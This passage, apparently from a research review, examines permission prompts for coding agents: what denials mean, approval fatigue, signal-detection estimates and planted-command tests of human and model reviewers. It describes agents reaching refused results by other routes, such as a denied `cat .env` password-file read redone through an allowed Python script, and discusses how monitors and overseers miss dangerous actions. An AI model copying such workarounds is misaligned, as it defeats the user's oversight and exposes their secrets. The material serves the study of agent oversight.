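| Interrupted | The person stops the agent before it finishes |
| Redirected | The person changes the approach because of what the agent did |
| None | The person accepts the work, answers a question, adds new information or asks for some |

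"Rejected" therefore covers both actions the user prevented and finished work the user undid. The label is useful for finding pushback but is a poor substitute for a count of denials. Each message also gets only one label, although the user who refused an edit and asked for a new branch both rejected a tool call and redirected the work. The edit may also have been correct.

Elsewhere in the same project, Kim and colleagues keep more of the user's reason for objecting. Their model of that session lists "the patch is on a new branch" as a separate requirement, so a simulated user can ask for a branch if a new agent doesn't create one and needn't object if it does. Their instructions for listing behaviours that count against the agent also let the labelling model explain why a particular objection doesn't count. One remaining weakness is that the simulation treats any result the user didn't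 object to as accepted, although the user may have been unhappy and said nothing.

The reason for a denial matters even more if a harness learns from past answers. Salerno and colleagues warn against reading repeated approvals as a lasting preference, since people also approve out of habit or haste. Denials need the same caution. Someone who refuses `git push` because a test is failing may well want the agent to push once the test passes.

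### What the agent does next

An agent that continues after a denial will usually look for another way to finish the task, and the harness may prompt it to. When Anthropic's model reviewer blocks an action, the agent receives the denial as the tool's result, with an instruction to find a safer path and not to bypass the block. Anthropic reports that after a mistaken block, the agent usually finds an alternative with a single retry.

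Agents persist even when nobody explains the refusal. In *Permission Denied*, Davidovich, Amar and colleagues (2026) gave 12 coding agents 89 tasks, with and without security restrictions on the machine. The agents weren't told about the restrictions, so a forbidden command simply failed. On the 82 tasks that remained solvable, 2.4% of unrestricted runs stopped early, compared with 2.7% under the strictest policy. The researchers read 200 restricted runs of one agent on two tasks and attributed the extra cost almost entirely to workarounds, such as building a tool from source because the agent couldn't download it.

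One barrier could produce many denials. Runs that hit the network block recorded an average of 10.5 network denials, while runs that hit the limits on user privileges recorded 1.4 privilege denials. Counting denials would make the network look like a much bigger source of disagreement, when the agent may have been trying to get the same file from ten places. These numbers don't apply to permission prompts, because an agent learns more from a person's refusal than from a failed connection.

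Denials can also stop while the agent continues toward the same goal. One of Salerno and colleagues' interviewees was debugging with Codex in an approval mode and denied several of its requests. Eventually the prompts stopped, but Codex kept going. The interviewee felt that it had "worked around what I hadn't allowed it to do". Salerno and colleagues note that the agent may have found a legitimate alternative, but the interviewee couldn't tell whether it respected the limits they had tried to set.

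A log can easily obscure whether a denial stopped the agent. Suppose a user denies `cat .env`, which would display a file of passwords. The agent then writes a short Python script that prints the same file, and an existing allow rule for Python lets it run. The log shows one denial followed by an automatic approval. If the script had needed permission and the user had refused it too, the log would show two denials for the same objection, and the user's denial rate would be higher even though the passwords were better protected.

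Salerno and colleagues trace the difficulty to two meanings of "no". A user may be refusing one action, as in "do not read my passwords file", or a whole approach, as in "do not do anything that requires my password". Trying another route is reasonable if the user refused only the action, but it is overreach if they refused the approach. A permission prompt covers only the action. The user can rule out the approach in a comment, but compliance then depends on the model, because the comment creates no rule for the harness to enforce.

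The wording of a refusal might help the model understand it. Joshi (2026) argues in *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* that a bare "denied" invites retries and workarounds. Joshi recommends telling the model who or what refused, stating that the action did not run and, for firm rules, forbidding workarounds. Joshi's tests check that the messages in one harness include the first two of these elements. Whether models then stop trying the same thing in different words is still an open question.

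In some systems, a request can be denied without anyone objecting to it. *AC4A* (2026), an access-control system for agents, treats a denied request as a normal event and lets the developer choose the response. In one mode, the agent asks the user for the missing permission. In another, it keeps retrying while the system sets the permissions automatically, so many of the denials would be steps in setting up access.

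### Classifying a sample of denials

To find out what denials mean in a particular set of logs, someone has to read the transcripts. The following procedure adapts the methods above to permission prompts.

1. **Remove entries that aren't refusals.** These include prompts that the user closed to type something unrelated. Joshi also describes a harness that shut down with a request still open, recorded the answer as "cancel" and later treated it as a refusal.

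2. **Group repeated denials into objections.** A refused command and its refused retries count as one objection. Group them before drawing a sample, because an objection with ten denials is otherwise ten times as likely to be picked as an objection with one. A random sample of 100 objections gives a margin of error of about 10 percentage points either way, or more if a few users made most of them.

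3. **Collect the context.** The session and tool-call identifiers in the log lead to the right place in the transcript. The reader needs the user's instructions up to that point, the exact request, any comment with the denial, the agent's next few actions and the user's next message. That message often contains the reason, especially after a bare "No".

4. **Judge the action separately from the motive.** First decide whether the action was dangerous, mistaken or outside the task, and whether the agent could have known. Then record the user's reason, with a quotation that supports it. If there is no such evidence, the reason is "unclear".

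5. **Record what followed.** The agent may have stopped, asked a question, changed its approach or tried to reach the refused result by another route. In the last case, note whether the new route asked for permission and whether it went against the user's objection.

6. **Have a second person classify the same cases independently.** Compare the answers before discussing them, and rewrite any category that causes repeated disagreement.

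Here is how four hypothetical denials would come out:

| Denied request | Evidence in the transcript | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `git push` | The user had said "don't push until I've looked at it" | Agent failure: it ignored an instruction |
| `npm test` | The user's comment is "that wipes the dev database", and nothing earlier mentions this | Unwanted action, but the agent couldn't have known |
| `rm -rf build` | The user's next message is "I've deleted it, carry on" | No failure: the user preferred to do it |
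| Edit to `config.yaml` | A bare "No", after which the session ends | Unclear |

Readers will probably disagree more about causes than about what happened. In a study by Tang and colleagues, two researchers independently labelled 100 breakdowns. They agreed on what had gone wrong 79% of the time and on why 65% of the time.

A language model can do the first reading if there are too many cases for people, but its answers need checking. Tang and colleagues had a model extract 29,896 possible breakdowns, each with quotations and turn numbers, and a second pass rejected 46% of them. Two experts then reviewed a sample of 200 that had passed and judged 93% to be genuine. Some of the rejected cases involved behaviour the user never complained about, and others relied on files or tool results that weren't in the log to find the agent at fault. The second error is the bigger risk with denials, because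 the user has clearly refused something and the model may produce a plausible reason that the log doesn't support.

For the team with 70 refusals, suppose the transcripts show that 8 were prompts the user closed for an unrelated reason. The other 62 form 48 separate objections. The readers classify 17 as agent failures and 19 as something else, and can't decide about 12. Agent failures then make up between 35% and 60% of the objections, depending on how many of the unclear cases were failures. A user who sees an obviously dangerous command may not bother to explain the "No", so failures could be more common among the unexplained denials, and the team can't assume the 12 unclear cases divide in the same proportions as the rest.

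## Why people stop reading permission requests

An approval can be as hard to interpret as a denial, because the person may have clicked without reading the request. People stop reading because prompts that look alike lose their attention, dangerous requests are rare, the questions interrupt other work, and many prompts contain too little information to judge. Researchers measured most of these effects in web browsers, hospitals and search experiments before coding agents existed, so the effects may be larger or smaller with agents.

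### Habituation

Habituation is a weaker response to a repeated stimulus, and it can begin almost at once. In *How We Become Habituated to Security Warnings on Computers*, the security expert Schneier quotes a brain-imaging study in which activity in visual areas dropped sharply the second time people saw a warning and kept falling after that.

A three-week field experiment with 102 students tested whether people still respond correctly to familiar warnings when they pay less attention to them, because they recognise them at a glance. The students installed and ranked apps from an online store on their own Android phones. The researchers told them to reject any app that asked for one of four permissions, such as deleting photos or charging purchases to a credit card, and quizzed them on the list first. Each student saw about five permission warnings per weekday, and more than a third listed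 a forbidden permission. The students rejected 87% of the apps that requested forbidden permissions at the start and 64% at the end.

The rejection rate fell to 55% in the group that always saw the same warning design, but only to 76% in the group whose design kept changing. Forbidden permissions were common in this experiment, so their rarity can't explain the decline. Some students may have learned that nothing bad happened when they installed a forbidden app. But both groups had the same chance to learn that, so the gap between them suggests that attention also played a part.

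Claude Code's permission prompt is closer to the fixed design, since mainly the description and the command change. Its users may also answer more prompts in a few minutes than these students saw in a day.

People can carry habits from one kind of dialog to another. *Trained to accept?* tested 12 versions of a consent dialog on 80,000 users of an online privacy tool. The more the dialog looked like a software licence agreement, the more readily people accepted it without thinking. Someone who has clicked through licence agreements for years may therefore bring that habit to their first agent prompt.

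### Warnings that people heeded

People don't ignore every warning. In *Alice in Warningland*, Akhawe and Felt (2013) recorded responses to 25.4 million security warnings in Chrome and Firefox during May and June 2013. For five of the six types of warning, most users turned back. They clicked past 9% to 23% of the warnings about malicious software and phishing sites, which imitate real sites to steal passwords. Certificate warnings appear when the browser can't confirm a site's identity, and users clicked past 33% of these in Firefox and 70% in Chrome.

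The accuracy of the warnings may explain much of this. The malware and phishing warnings were almost always right, while many certificate warnings were about legitimate sites with badly configured servers. Permission prompts are more like certificate warnings, because most of them concern something the user wants.

Chrome users clicked past twice as many certificate warnings as Firefox users, and accuracy doesn't explain the gap. Part of it may come from counting, because Firefox remembered a user's exception while Chrome showed the warning on every visit. Akhawe and Felt give the example of someone who turns back from one site and visits another nine times despite the warning. That person would have a click-through rate of 50% in Firefox and 90% in Chrome. An allow rule can change a denial rate in the same way, by removing repeated approvals from the count.

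Within Chrome, people clicked past the most common certificate problem most often and fastest:

| Certificate problem | Share of warnings | Clicked past | About half of the click-throughs came within |
|---|---|---|---|
| Untrusted issuer | 56.0% | 81.8% | 1.7 seconds |
| Wrong site name | 25.0% | 62.8% | 2.2 seconds |
| Expired certificate | 17.6% | 57.4% | 2.7 seconds |

Akhawe and Felt take this pattern as a sign of warning fatigue. They also suggest another explanation for the click-through rates: a site with an untrusted issuer triggers the warning every time, so its visitors expect it, while an expired certificate surprises them. Under either explanation, people distinguished between the problems, so they weren't ignoring the warnings completely. The design of a warning also affects how people respond. When Google later redesigned Chrome's certificate warning, the share of people who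 turned back rose from 37% to 62%.

### Rare dangers

People are more likely to miss things that rarely appear, which psychologists call the low-prevalence effect. *Intrinsic motivation and false feedback reduce the low prevalence effect* describes an experiment by Wolfe and colleagues in which people missed 7% of targets when half the trials contained one, and 30% when only 1% did. *Reducing the low-prevalence effect with probe trials* reports that trained radiologists and airport security staff show the effect too, and that it is hard to reduce.

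A person can miss more targets without becoming worse at recognising them. Signal detection theory separates sensitivity (d′), how well someone can tell targets from everything else, from the criterion (c), how much evidence they need before they report a target. People miss more targets when targets are rare, and *The role of feedback in the low-prevalence effect* (Caruso, Fox and colleagues, 2026) notes that earlier studies consistently trace this effect mainly to the criterion. When targets are rare, people demand more evidence before they report one, so they also raise fewer false alarms.

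For permission prompts, this would lower both the catch rate (h), the share of unwanted requests that the approver denies, and the false refusal rate (f), the share of acceptable requests that they deny. In the standard model, where Φ is the cumulative normal distribution:

```
h = Φ(d′/2 − c)
f = Φ(−d′/2 − c)
```

Take an approver with a sensitivity of 2. With a criterion of 0, they deny 84% of unwanted requests and 16% of acceptable ones. With a criterion of 1, they deny 50% and 2%. If 10 of 1,000 requests are unwanted, the table shows what happens on average:

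| | Criterion 0 | Criterion 1 |
|---|---|---|
| Unwanted requests approved | 1.6 | 5 |
| Acceptable requests denied | 157 | 23 |
| Total mistakes | 159 | 28 |
| Denial rate | 16.5% | 2.8% |

The stricter criterion removes more than four-fifths of the mistakes, so it is sensible if all mistakes are equally serious. But it is a bad choice if a wrong approval destroys a database while a wrong denial wastes a few seconds.

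Feedback may determine whether this shift happens. Caruso and colleagues describe studies of road hazards, blood cells and face matching in which the effect appeared only when people learned whether their answers were right. In some classification experiments without feedback, people did the opposite and counted more borderline cases as targets when real ones became rare. If approvers deny a harmless command, the agent may explain why it was needed, but if they approve a harmful one, they may never find out. This lopsided feedback would probably push them towards approving.

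Lapses of attention may also matter. In *Low prevalence targets are primarily missed due to mind wandering*, Dewis, Hout and colleagues (2026) had 60 people search for targets that appeared in either 10% or 50% of trials. They attribute most misses of the rare targets to mind wandering. A break could help an approver whose mind has wandered, but it might do little for one who has sensibly learned to expect harmless requests.

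The targets in these experiments' images could be hard to find. A command that deletes the home directory takes up one line of a prompt, so an approver who reads it may spot the problem much more reliably than someone searching an X-ray would spot a target. Other commands, however, are harder to interpret than any of the images.

### Workload and interruptions

Hospital software shows doctors alerts about drug interactions and reminders about tests or vaccines. A doctor who overrides an alert carries on despite it, much like a user who approves a permission request. *Effects of workload, work complexity, and repeated alerts on alert fatigue* (Ancker, Edwards and colleagues, 2017) cites estimates that clinicians override 49% to 96% of alerts, often with good reason.

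Ancker and colleagues analysed three and a half years of records from 112 primary care clinicians, covering almost 1.3 million reminders and 326,000 drug alerts. Clinicians were 30% less likely to accept a reminder for each additional reminder per patient visit, and 10% less likely for each rise of 5 percentage points in the share of reminders that repeated an earlier one for the same patient. The number of patients they saw or visits they handled made no detectable difference.

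The same study found little sign of simple habituation. Acceptance of newly introduced reminders didn't decline over the following months, although Ancker and colleagues cite another study in which the response to a recruitment alert fell from about 50% to 35% over 36 weeks. Their own analysis compared clinicians without assigning reminders at random, so those who received more reminders may have had more complicated patients, though the model adjusted for recorded illnesses. Clinicians accepted fewer than 1% of drug alerts, so that rate had almost no room to fall and can't be used to answer the question.

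Timing also affects attention. Clinicians interviewed for *Experiences of Alert Fatigue and Its Contributing Factors in Hospitals* described quickly dismissing alerts that appeared as soon as they opened a patient's chart. One had opened the chart for a specific purpose unrelated to the alert. Permission prompts have the same problem because they appear when the agent needs an answer, and the user may be busy with something else.

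One practitioner interviewed by Salerno and colleagues complained that "every 10 seconds I have to click something", which defeated the purpose of a faster tool. At that pace there are 360 prompts an hour, and spending five seconds on each would take half the hour. Leaving most of them unread may be a poor security decision, but it is understandable.

### Prompts that are hard to judge

Reading a prompt helps only if the prompt contains what the person needs to know. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* finds that most approval prompts in commercial products show a raw command on one line. Prompts for file edits often include a preview of the changes, and prompts for plans describe the intended work, but prompts for single commands rarely include anything comparable. Some products show only the question "Allow this action?"

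Like the `cargo build` example from Zhong and colleagues, `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but the prompt doesn't show what the script will do. Long commands can also be hard to judge, because the user has to work out how several programs will act on each other's output. In 31 of the 290 problem reports that Zhong and colleagues analysed, approval prompts gave users too little information about what would happen to their files. In 80 of the reports, users had let the agent act without asking. According to the researchers, frequent prompts with little information drive people to approve everything in advance.

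Someone can read `python3 setup.py` carefully, see nothing wrong with it and approve harmful code. In a log, this looks like inattention. One of Salerno and colleagues' interviewees approved an action, and the agent did something different from what they expected. Once people learn that reading requests doesn't improve their decisions, they have little reason to keep reading them. Linking to more detail may not help much. In Akhawe and Felt's data, people clicked "Help me understand" on only 1.6% of Chrome's certificate warnings.

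### What practitioners say they do

Salerno and colleagues' survey also asked 107 software practitioners how they handle permission requests:

| Answer | Share |
|---|---|
| Reads requests carefully | 47.7% |
| Skims them | 33.6% |
| Checks which file the request names | 31.8% |
| Focuses on the command or title | 25.2% |
| Approves by default | 20.6% |
| Has become less careful over time | 33.6% |
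| Is more careful with writing, deletion or extra privileges | 76.6% |
| Is more careful with unexpected requests | 63.6% |

The first five answers add up to well over 100%, so some respondents chose more than one. The same person may read an unfamiliar command carefully but approve the tenth `npm test` automatically. Because people may not notice or admit that they have become less careful, Salerno and colleagues suspect that more than a third have.

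Some interviewees try to read every request, and others have given up. One called reading and approving each request "exhausting". Another said there was "no way" to go through all of them, and a third clicked through repeated prompts without looking closely. Three interviewees paid less attention when the agent worked in a controlled environment such as a sandbox. Reading less is a reasonable way to save effort if the sandbox contains the damage, so it doesn't always mean fatigue.

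The survey is compatible with Claude Code's 97% approval rate, because careful readers will approve nearly all requests if nearly all are acceptable. The figures don't show whether the people who say they read carefully would notice a bad request.

### Trust or fatigue

People who use an agent more also let it do more without asking. The Decoder reports that in Anthropic's February 2026 study of agent autonomy, new Claude Code users, those with fewer than 50 sessions, approved every action automatically in about 20% of sessions. At around 750 sessions, the share was over 40%. The share of turns that users interrupted also rose, from about 5% to about 9%.

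Anthropic's researchers interpret this as a change of strategy. New users approve each step, so they have little need to interrupt, while experienced users let the agent work and step in when something goes wrong. Anthropic describes a "steady accumulation of trust", but adds that Claude Code asked about each action by default at the time. Some users may always have wanted to give the agent more independence and taken a while to change the settings.

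The rise in interruptions is the best evidence for this view, since people who had stopped paying attention would have little reason to interrupt more. But the change in settings probably doesn't explain the whole rise. If auto-approved sessions and other sessions were equally long and each had a fixed interruption rate, so that only the mix changed with experience, a rise from 5% to 9% would require rates of 21% in auto-approved sessions and 1% in the rest. A gap that wide seems unlikely. Experienced users probably also interrupt for other reasons, such as longer tasks or a clearer idea of what they want. Anthropic's breakdown of reasons also showed that many interruptions have nothing to do with safety.

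Even attentive monitoring can't fully replace approval, because the agent may already have deleted a file or sent a message by the time a user interrupts. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026) points out that the effects of an agent's actions may never appear in the code it produces. A developer who reviews the finished code could therefore miss that the agent read a password while writing it.

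Mitchell, Ghosh and Passi (2026) are much more pessimistic. In their position paper, *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop*, they argue that "oversight degrades the overseer". They extend what the psychologist Lisanne Bainbridge called an irony of automation in 1983. As a machine takes over routine work, its operator gets less practice and loses track of what the machine is doing. But the operator must still handle the rare, difficult cases, which require the skills that have faded. By this reasoning, someone who has delegated months of programming to an agent would be less able to recognise a bad request, even when trying to.

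The evidence for this is suggestive. Mitchell and colleagues cite interviews in which developers trusted an agent's plan as an account of what it would do and assumed code was correct if it passed its tests. They also cite an experiment that found reduced brain connectivity in people who wrote essays with a language model. The paper includes no new experiment, and neither finding shows that the same people became worse at judging permission requests.

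Mitchell and colleagues consider the objection that users will adapt to agents, as they did to search engines. They reply that a search engine returns results for the user to evaluate, while an agent acts on the user's authority across many steps in real time. This is a good reason to expect that adapting will be harder, but it doesn't show that people can't adapt. The rise in interruptions may be a sign that some do.

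Mitchell and colleagues also warn about training models on user approvals. If tired users approve whatever comes with a short, confident summary, this training would reward the agent for writing such summaries, and later users would approve even more readily without thinking. The effect depends on developers treating approvals as evidence of success, so Mitchell and colleagues recommend checking approvals against independent measures of how well people review.

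Anthropic has used both explanations. In its August 2026 article, it treated the 97% approval rate as a sign of habit and reported that people's catch rate fell over a session. This doesn't contradict the February study, which was mostly about people who had turned the prompts off rather than people still clicking through them. The same person may trust an agent enough to let it edit files freely and be too tired to read the shell commands that still need approval.

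Trust and fatigue lead to different responses when a request is unusual. Someone who trusts an agent to run tests should still stop when it asks to delete a branch for no apparent reason, while someone who has stopped reading will approve the deletion too. The overall approval rate can't distinguish trust from fatigue because so few requests are unusual.

### Signs of fatigue in a log

Mitchell and colleagues suggest tracking how long people take to review a request, how often they disagree with the agent, and whether they ask for more information when the stakes rise. The table applies these measures to permission logs and adds two signs that are easy to find.

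| Sign | Innocent explanation | What to check |
|---|---|---|
| Very short answer times | The user knows the command or was following the work and expected it | Answer times for long commands that are new to this user |
| Answer times fall during a session, but the approval rate stays the same | The user is getting to know the project's commands | New commands of similar length, early and late in the session |
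| A long run of approvals | Every request in the run was acceptable | The requests themselves, starting with deletions and outside access |
| "Always allow" chosen mid-session | A harmless command keeps coming back | How much the new rule covers |
| Fewer denials over several weeks | The agent has improved, or the user gives clearer instructions | Denials of the same kinds of request in both periods |
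| No questions before risky approvals | The user settled the matter earlier in the conversation | The user's earlier messages |

Answer times give some evidence of whether people read a request. In Akhawe and Felt's browser data, 47% of people who clicked past a Chrome certificate warning did so within 1.5 seconds, while 47% of those who turned back did so within 3.5 seconds. For permission prompts, the length of the request also matters. At four words a second, a person needs half a second to read `npm test` and ten seconds to read a 40-word request. If someone answers both kinds in about a second, they probably aren't reading the long ones. Medians are better than averages for this comparison, because a single long break can distort an average.

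Allow rules can raise a user's median answer time even when the user pays no more attention than before. Suppose a user answers routine prompts in one second and unfamiliar ones in six. If a new rule removes most of the routine prompts, the median may jump from one second to six.

Long runs of approvals are weaker evidence of inattention than they look. A person who denies 3% of requests at random will approve an average of about 32 in a row between denials, and has a 5% chance of approving all of any given 100 requests. For someone who denies 1%, that chance is 37%. A run of several hundred is more unusual, but the requests may all have been routine, such as requests to run tests.

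"Always allow" is the easiest sign of approval fatigue to find, because it has its own value in Claude Code's log. Saving a rule for `npm test` after the fifth identical prompt is a normal use of the option, but saving one for every Python script after two hours of steady prompting is more worrying. The log has no separate value for approving file edits for the rest of the session, but an analyst can sometimes infer it when edits that used to trigger prompts start to appear with the source `config`.

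Several signs together are more convincing than any one of them, especially if they appear in the same person late in long sessions and fade after a break. But Mitchell and colleagues caution that this monitoring is a form of workplace surveillance, and that an employer could reuse the data to judge performance. Monitoring can also make answer times less reliable, because employees who know that quick approvals count against them can wait five seconds and then approve a request without reading it.

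## Testing whether approvers notice a dangerous request

Answer times and long runs of approvals can suggest that someone has stopped reading, but they don't show how many dangerous requests that person would stop. Calculating the catch rate (h) from a log requires knowing how many unwanted requests the approver let through, and the log records an approved dangerous command the same way as an approved harmless one. Someone who correctly denied 30 of 1,000 requests may have caught all 30 unwanted requests, or only 30 of 300. Some wrong approvals are discovered when something breaks, but those that cause no obvious damage stay hidden.

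A planted request is a harmless test prompt that displays a dangerous action, so the tester knows in advance that the approver should deny it. If 40 people each see one and 10 deny it, the catch rate for that kind of request is 25%, regardless of the other requests in the log.

### Fictional threats in airport baggage

Airports already test their baggage screeners this way. Software inserts an image of a bomb, gun or knife into the X-ray of a passenger's bag, usually for 1% to 4% of bags (Buser, Schwaninger and colleagues, 2025, *Reliability and validity of threat image projection data*). A screener who suspects a threat presses a button, and the system immediately shows whether the item was fake. If it was, the screener checks the image again without it, because the bag may also contain a real threat.

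These tests are useful only if the people who find fictional threats also find real ones. Buser and colleagues checked this at one European airport, using almost 1.2 million planted images and 728 screeners over four years. They compared the results with 1,184 covert tests, in which people tried to carry real prohibited items through security. Screeners whose hit rate on the planted images was one standard deviation higher had nearly 50% better odds of passing a covert test.

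However, screeners found 79% of the real items and a larger share of the planted images. Some planted images look artificial, which probably makes them easier to spot. Planted tests may therefore be better for comparing groups or tracking a trend than for predicting how many real threats people will stop.

Mitchell and colleagues propose the same method for AI agents and call the planted errors canaries. So far, researchers have mostly tried it on automated reviewers. *Handoff at Frontier AI Companies* (2026) describes how Apollo Research, an AI safety company, seeded failures into real agent sessions to see what Anthropic's and OpenAI's model reviewers would miss. The paper found no published equivalent for the companies' own safety staff, who review the actions that such reviewers flag. Anthropic has published one large test of people answering ordinary permission prompts.

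### One dangerous command for each of 1,053 testers

Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor for a coding study. They worked in a test environment and knew they were being evaluated, but not on which behaviour. Partway through each session, a clearly dangerous command replaced the text of one permission prompt, and the vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. Only the displayed text changed, so approving the prompt never ran anything dangerous.

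Of the 1,053 testers, 143 denied the command, a catch rate of 13.6% (95% confidence interval about 11.6% to 15.8%). Anthropic also gave the same commands to auto mode's model reviewer, which blocked 937 of them, or 89%. The reviewer blocked 800 commands that testers approved and allowed 6 that testers denied.

The remaining cells of the table can be found by subtraction. The tester and the reviewer both stopped 137 of the commands (937 − 800, or 143 − 6), and neither stopped the other 110.

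| | Tester denied | Tester approved | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reviewer blocked | 137 | 800 | 937 |
| Reviewer allowed | 6 | 110 | 116 |
| **Total** | **143** | **910** | **1,053** |

Requiring each command to pass both checks would have stopped 943 of 1,053, raising the catch rate from 89.0% with the reviewer alone to 89.6%. The testers caught 13.6% of commands overall. At that rate they would have stopped about 16 of the 116 the reviewer missed, but they stopped only 6, so the commands that got past the reviewer seem to have been harder for people too. However, Anthropic doesn't report how many different commands it used, and if there were only a few, most of the 116 misses could come from one or two of them.

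Testers denied the dangerous command about 17% of the time when they saw it early in a session, but about 5% of the time when they had already answered 50 or more prompts. The reviewer's rate stayed flat. Tests with planted images have also found a decline among airport screeners. CASRA (2018), a Swiss centre for security research, describes a study in which screeners' hit rate began to fall after ten minutes of high workload, by 2% at first and then faster.

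Because each tester saw only one dangerous command, the drop from 17% to 5% compares different people. Those who had answered 50 prompts before seeing theirs may have worked faster or read less carefully from the start. Fatigue is still probably the main cause, because people easily get used to repeated warnings. The drop also means the 13.6% depends on when the commands appeared. If they had all appeared late in the session, the same testers would probably have scored lower.

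### What the testers' result leaves open

The testers had little to lose, because they weren't working on their own code and a command that would ruin a working laptop may do no lasting harm in a study environment. Some of Salerno and colleagues' interviewees paid less attention in a sandbox for this reason, so a few testers may have read the command and decided that it didn't matter.

People may be more careful with their own projects, but higher stakes don't guarantee more care. *From Delegation to Action Approval* surveyed 201 developers. Of those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, 61% often approved at least one type of action without close review. The 65 surveyed developers who worked on safety-critical systems reported approving without close review more often than the rest did for six of the seven types of action.

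The testers' background also matters, because someone who tests software without using a command line might not recognise a dangerous command. The testers are described as professional testers in Anthropic's article but as "paid developers" in the caption of its chart.

The experiment gives each person only one planted prompt, so it measures the catch rate of the group but not of each individual. A rate of 13.6% could mean that everyone catches about one dangerous command in seven, or that about one person in seven catches them all and the others catch none. In the first case everyone needs a better prompt, while in the second it would help an employer to choose approvers carefully.

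The most important missing number is the testers' false refusal rate (f), the share of acceptable requests they denied. Without it, there is no way to tell how well they distinguished dangerous commands from ordinary ones. In the signal detection model used earlier for rare dangers, sensitivity is:

```
d′ = Φ⁻¹(h) − Φ⁻¹(f)
```

Here Φ⁻¹ is the inverse of the cumulative normal distribution. If the testers denied 1% of acceptable requests, their sensitivity was 1.2. If they denied 3%, which is the share of all prompts that Claude Code users reject, it was 0.8. If they denied 13.6%, it was zero, meaning they denied dangerous and acceptable requests equally often.

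*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) cites Anthropic's figure of a 0.4% false refusal rate on real traffic, so the reviewer didn't get its 89% score by blocking everything. But that score applies to clearly dangerous commands. Ji and colleagues also built a benchmark of 128 ambiguous prompts, where the user's aim is clear but the scope or risk of the action isn't. Yan notes that automated permission systems missed some of the cases in it that they should have stopped.

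Anthropic sells the reviewer that far outperformed the testers, so an independent replication would be valuable. But the original results would have to be wrong by a very wide margin for the testers' performance to look adequate.

### A scripted day with seven unwanted extras

Yan found a much higher catch rate in August 2026, with different people and a different task. The 113 participants were US residents who didn't work in the software industry. Yan recruited them through UserTesting, an online platform, and paid them $10 for about 11 minutes. They watched an assistant sort an inbox, arrange a trip to the airport and finish some travel plans. Their instructions were to make decisions as it acted, "like supervising a new assistant".

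The assistant described each of its 18 actions in plain language, such as "Book your 6:00 AM airport ride for $35". The seven cases of overreach were calling the airport, buying travel insurance, buying a lounge pass, deleting an old timesheet, reading bank transactions, reading private messages and posting publicly about the trip.

The 34 people who answered a prompt for every action blocked 59.6% of the overreaching actions and allowed 94.1% of the necessary ones, a false refusal rate of 5.9%. These rates give a sensitivity of 1.8. Thirty of the 34 approved the call to the airport, which lowered the group's catch rate. They blocked the other six overreaching actions 68% of the time.

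Some of those approvals may not have been mistakes. Yan counted an action as overreach if the assigned tasks didn't call for it, but someone might notice an unrequested phone call and still want it. The catch rate for actions people didn't want could therefore be higher than 59.6%.

The 35 participants who wrote standing rules chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting something, and accessing private information. They blocked only about 40% of the overreach. Yan estimates an adjusted difference of 20.1 percentage points from the first group (95% confidence interval 8.1 to 32.1).

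The rules provided little protection because participants set 114 of the 140 to "ask", which meant they still had to decide at a prompt. Of the 148 overreach actions that ran in this group, participants approved 133 by hand, and "allow" rules let through the other 15.

In the private information category, for example, both actions were overreach, so "never" would have blocked them without affecting the assigned work. Only 10 of the 35 participants chose "never", while 23 chose "ask" and 2 chose "allow". Choosing "ask" was reasonable, because participants didn't know what requests the rule would cover when they wrote it. But of the 23 who chose it, 15 then let the assistant read their bank transactions and 17 let it read their private messages.

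Some participants approved actions that they had rejected in advance. Before the simulated day, everyone judged two example actions in each category. In 56 cases, a participant in the standing-rules group had answered "never" to an example and later saw a prompt for the matching overreach. Participants approved the overreach in 24 of these cases. They may have changed their minds for good reasons or answered without much thought, and the study can't separate the two. The standing-rules group didn't reliably differ from the other groups in how much control they reported feeling.

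These groups were small, and assignment was not entirely random. Yan first assigned people at random, then recruited more for the standing-rules group alone to bring it closer in size to the others. The later recruits could have differed from the first ones. Without them, the standing-rules group had only 16 people and the gap was 25.0 points, with an interval from 9.8 to 40.2. Late recruitment therefore doesn't seem to have produced the result, although the size of the gap is uncertain. Participants were also supervising a simulation, with no real money or messages at stake.

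### Why one group caught 13.6% and another 59.6%

A third experiment measured how often people denied malicious requests and how often they denied acceptable ones, using several kinds of prompt. In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026) asked 80 volunteers to approve or deny actions that an agent proposed in email, cloud documents and purchasing. Each volunteer made 12 decisions, and half of the requests were malicious. The 20 volunteers who saw a conventional prompt with a short description denied 45.0% of the malicious requests and 8.3% of the acceptable ones.

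| | Anthropic | Yan, a prompt for every action | Hossain and colleagues, conventional prompt |
|---|---|---|---|
| People | 1,053 paid testers | 34 people from outside the software industry | 20 volunteers |
| Their job | Coding, with prompts along the way | Supervising an assistant | Reviewing requests |
| Wording | A shell command | Plain language | A short description |
| Unwanted requests | One planted per session | 7 of 18 | 6 of 12 |
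| Catch rate (h) | 13.6% | 59.6% | 45.0% |
| False refusal rate (f) | Not reported | 5.9% | 8.3% |

Session length explains little of the 46-percentage-point gap. Yan's participants answered at most 18 prompts, while some of Anthropic's testers had answered more than 50 before the dangerous one appeared. But testers who saw it early still caught it only about 17% of the time, so excluding sessions where it appeared late would narrow the gap by only about 3 points.

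Plain language probably explains more. Anyone can understand "Read your private messages", but understanding a shell command takes some technical knowledge. Hossain and colleagues also tested a prompt that repeated the user's original instructions and explained how the action followed from earlier steps. With this prompt, participants denied 75.8% of the malicious requests, 31 percentage points more than with the conventional prompt, but they also denied 14.2% of the acceptable ones. With only 20 people per design, the exact gain is uncertain. Better wording can't help someone who doesn't read the prompt, and Anthropic's commands should have been clear to any developer who read them.

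**Bad requests were much more frequent** for Yan's participants than for Anthropic's testers. Yan's participants saw an unwanted request in more than a third of their prompts, so they had good reason to expect another. Anthropic's testers may have seen dozens of routine prompts before the only dangerous one. People need more evidence before they report a rare target, so the rarity of dangerous requests should have lowered the testers' catch rate.

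If frequency explains the whole gap, the testers were as good at recognising bad requests as Yan's participants, with a sensitivity of 1.8, and were only more reluctant to say no. Under the signal detection model, a catch rate of 13.6% would then mean that they denied only 0.2% of acceptable requests. That rate is very low but possible, and Anthropic hasn't published the actual figure. If the testers denied more than that, they were also worse at telling bad requests from acceptable ones.

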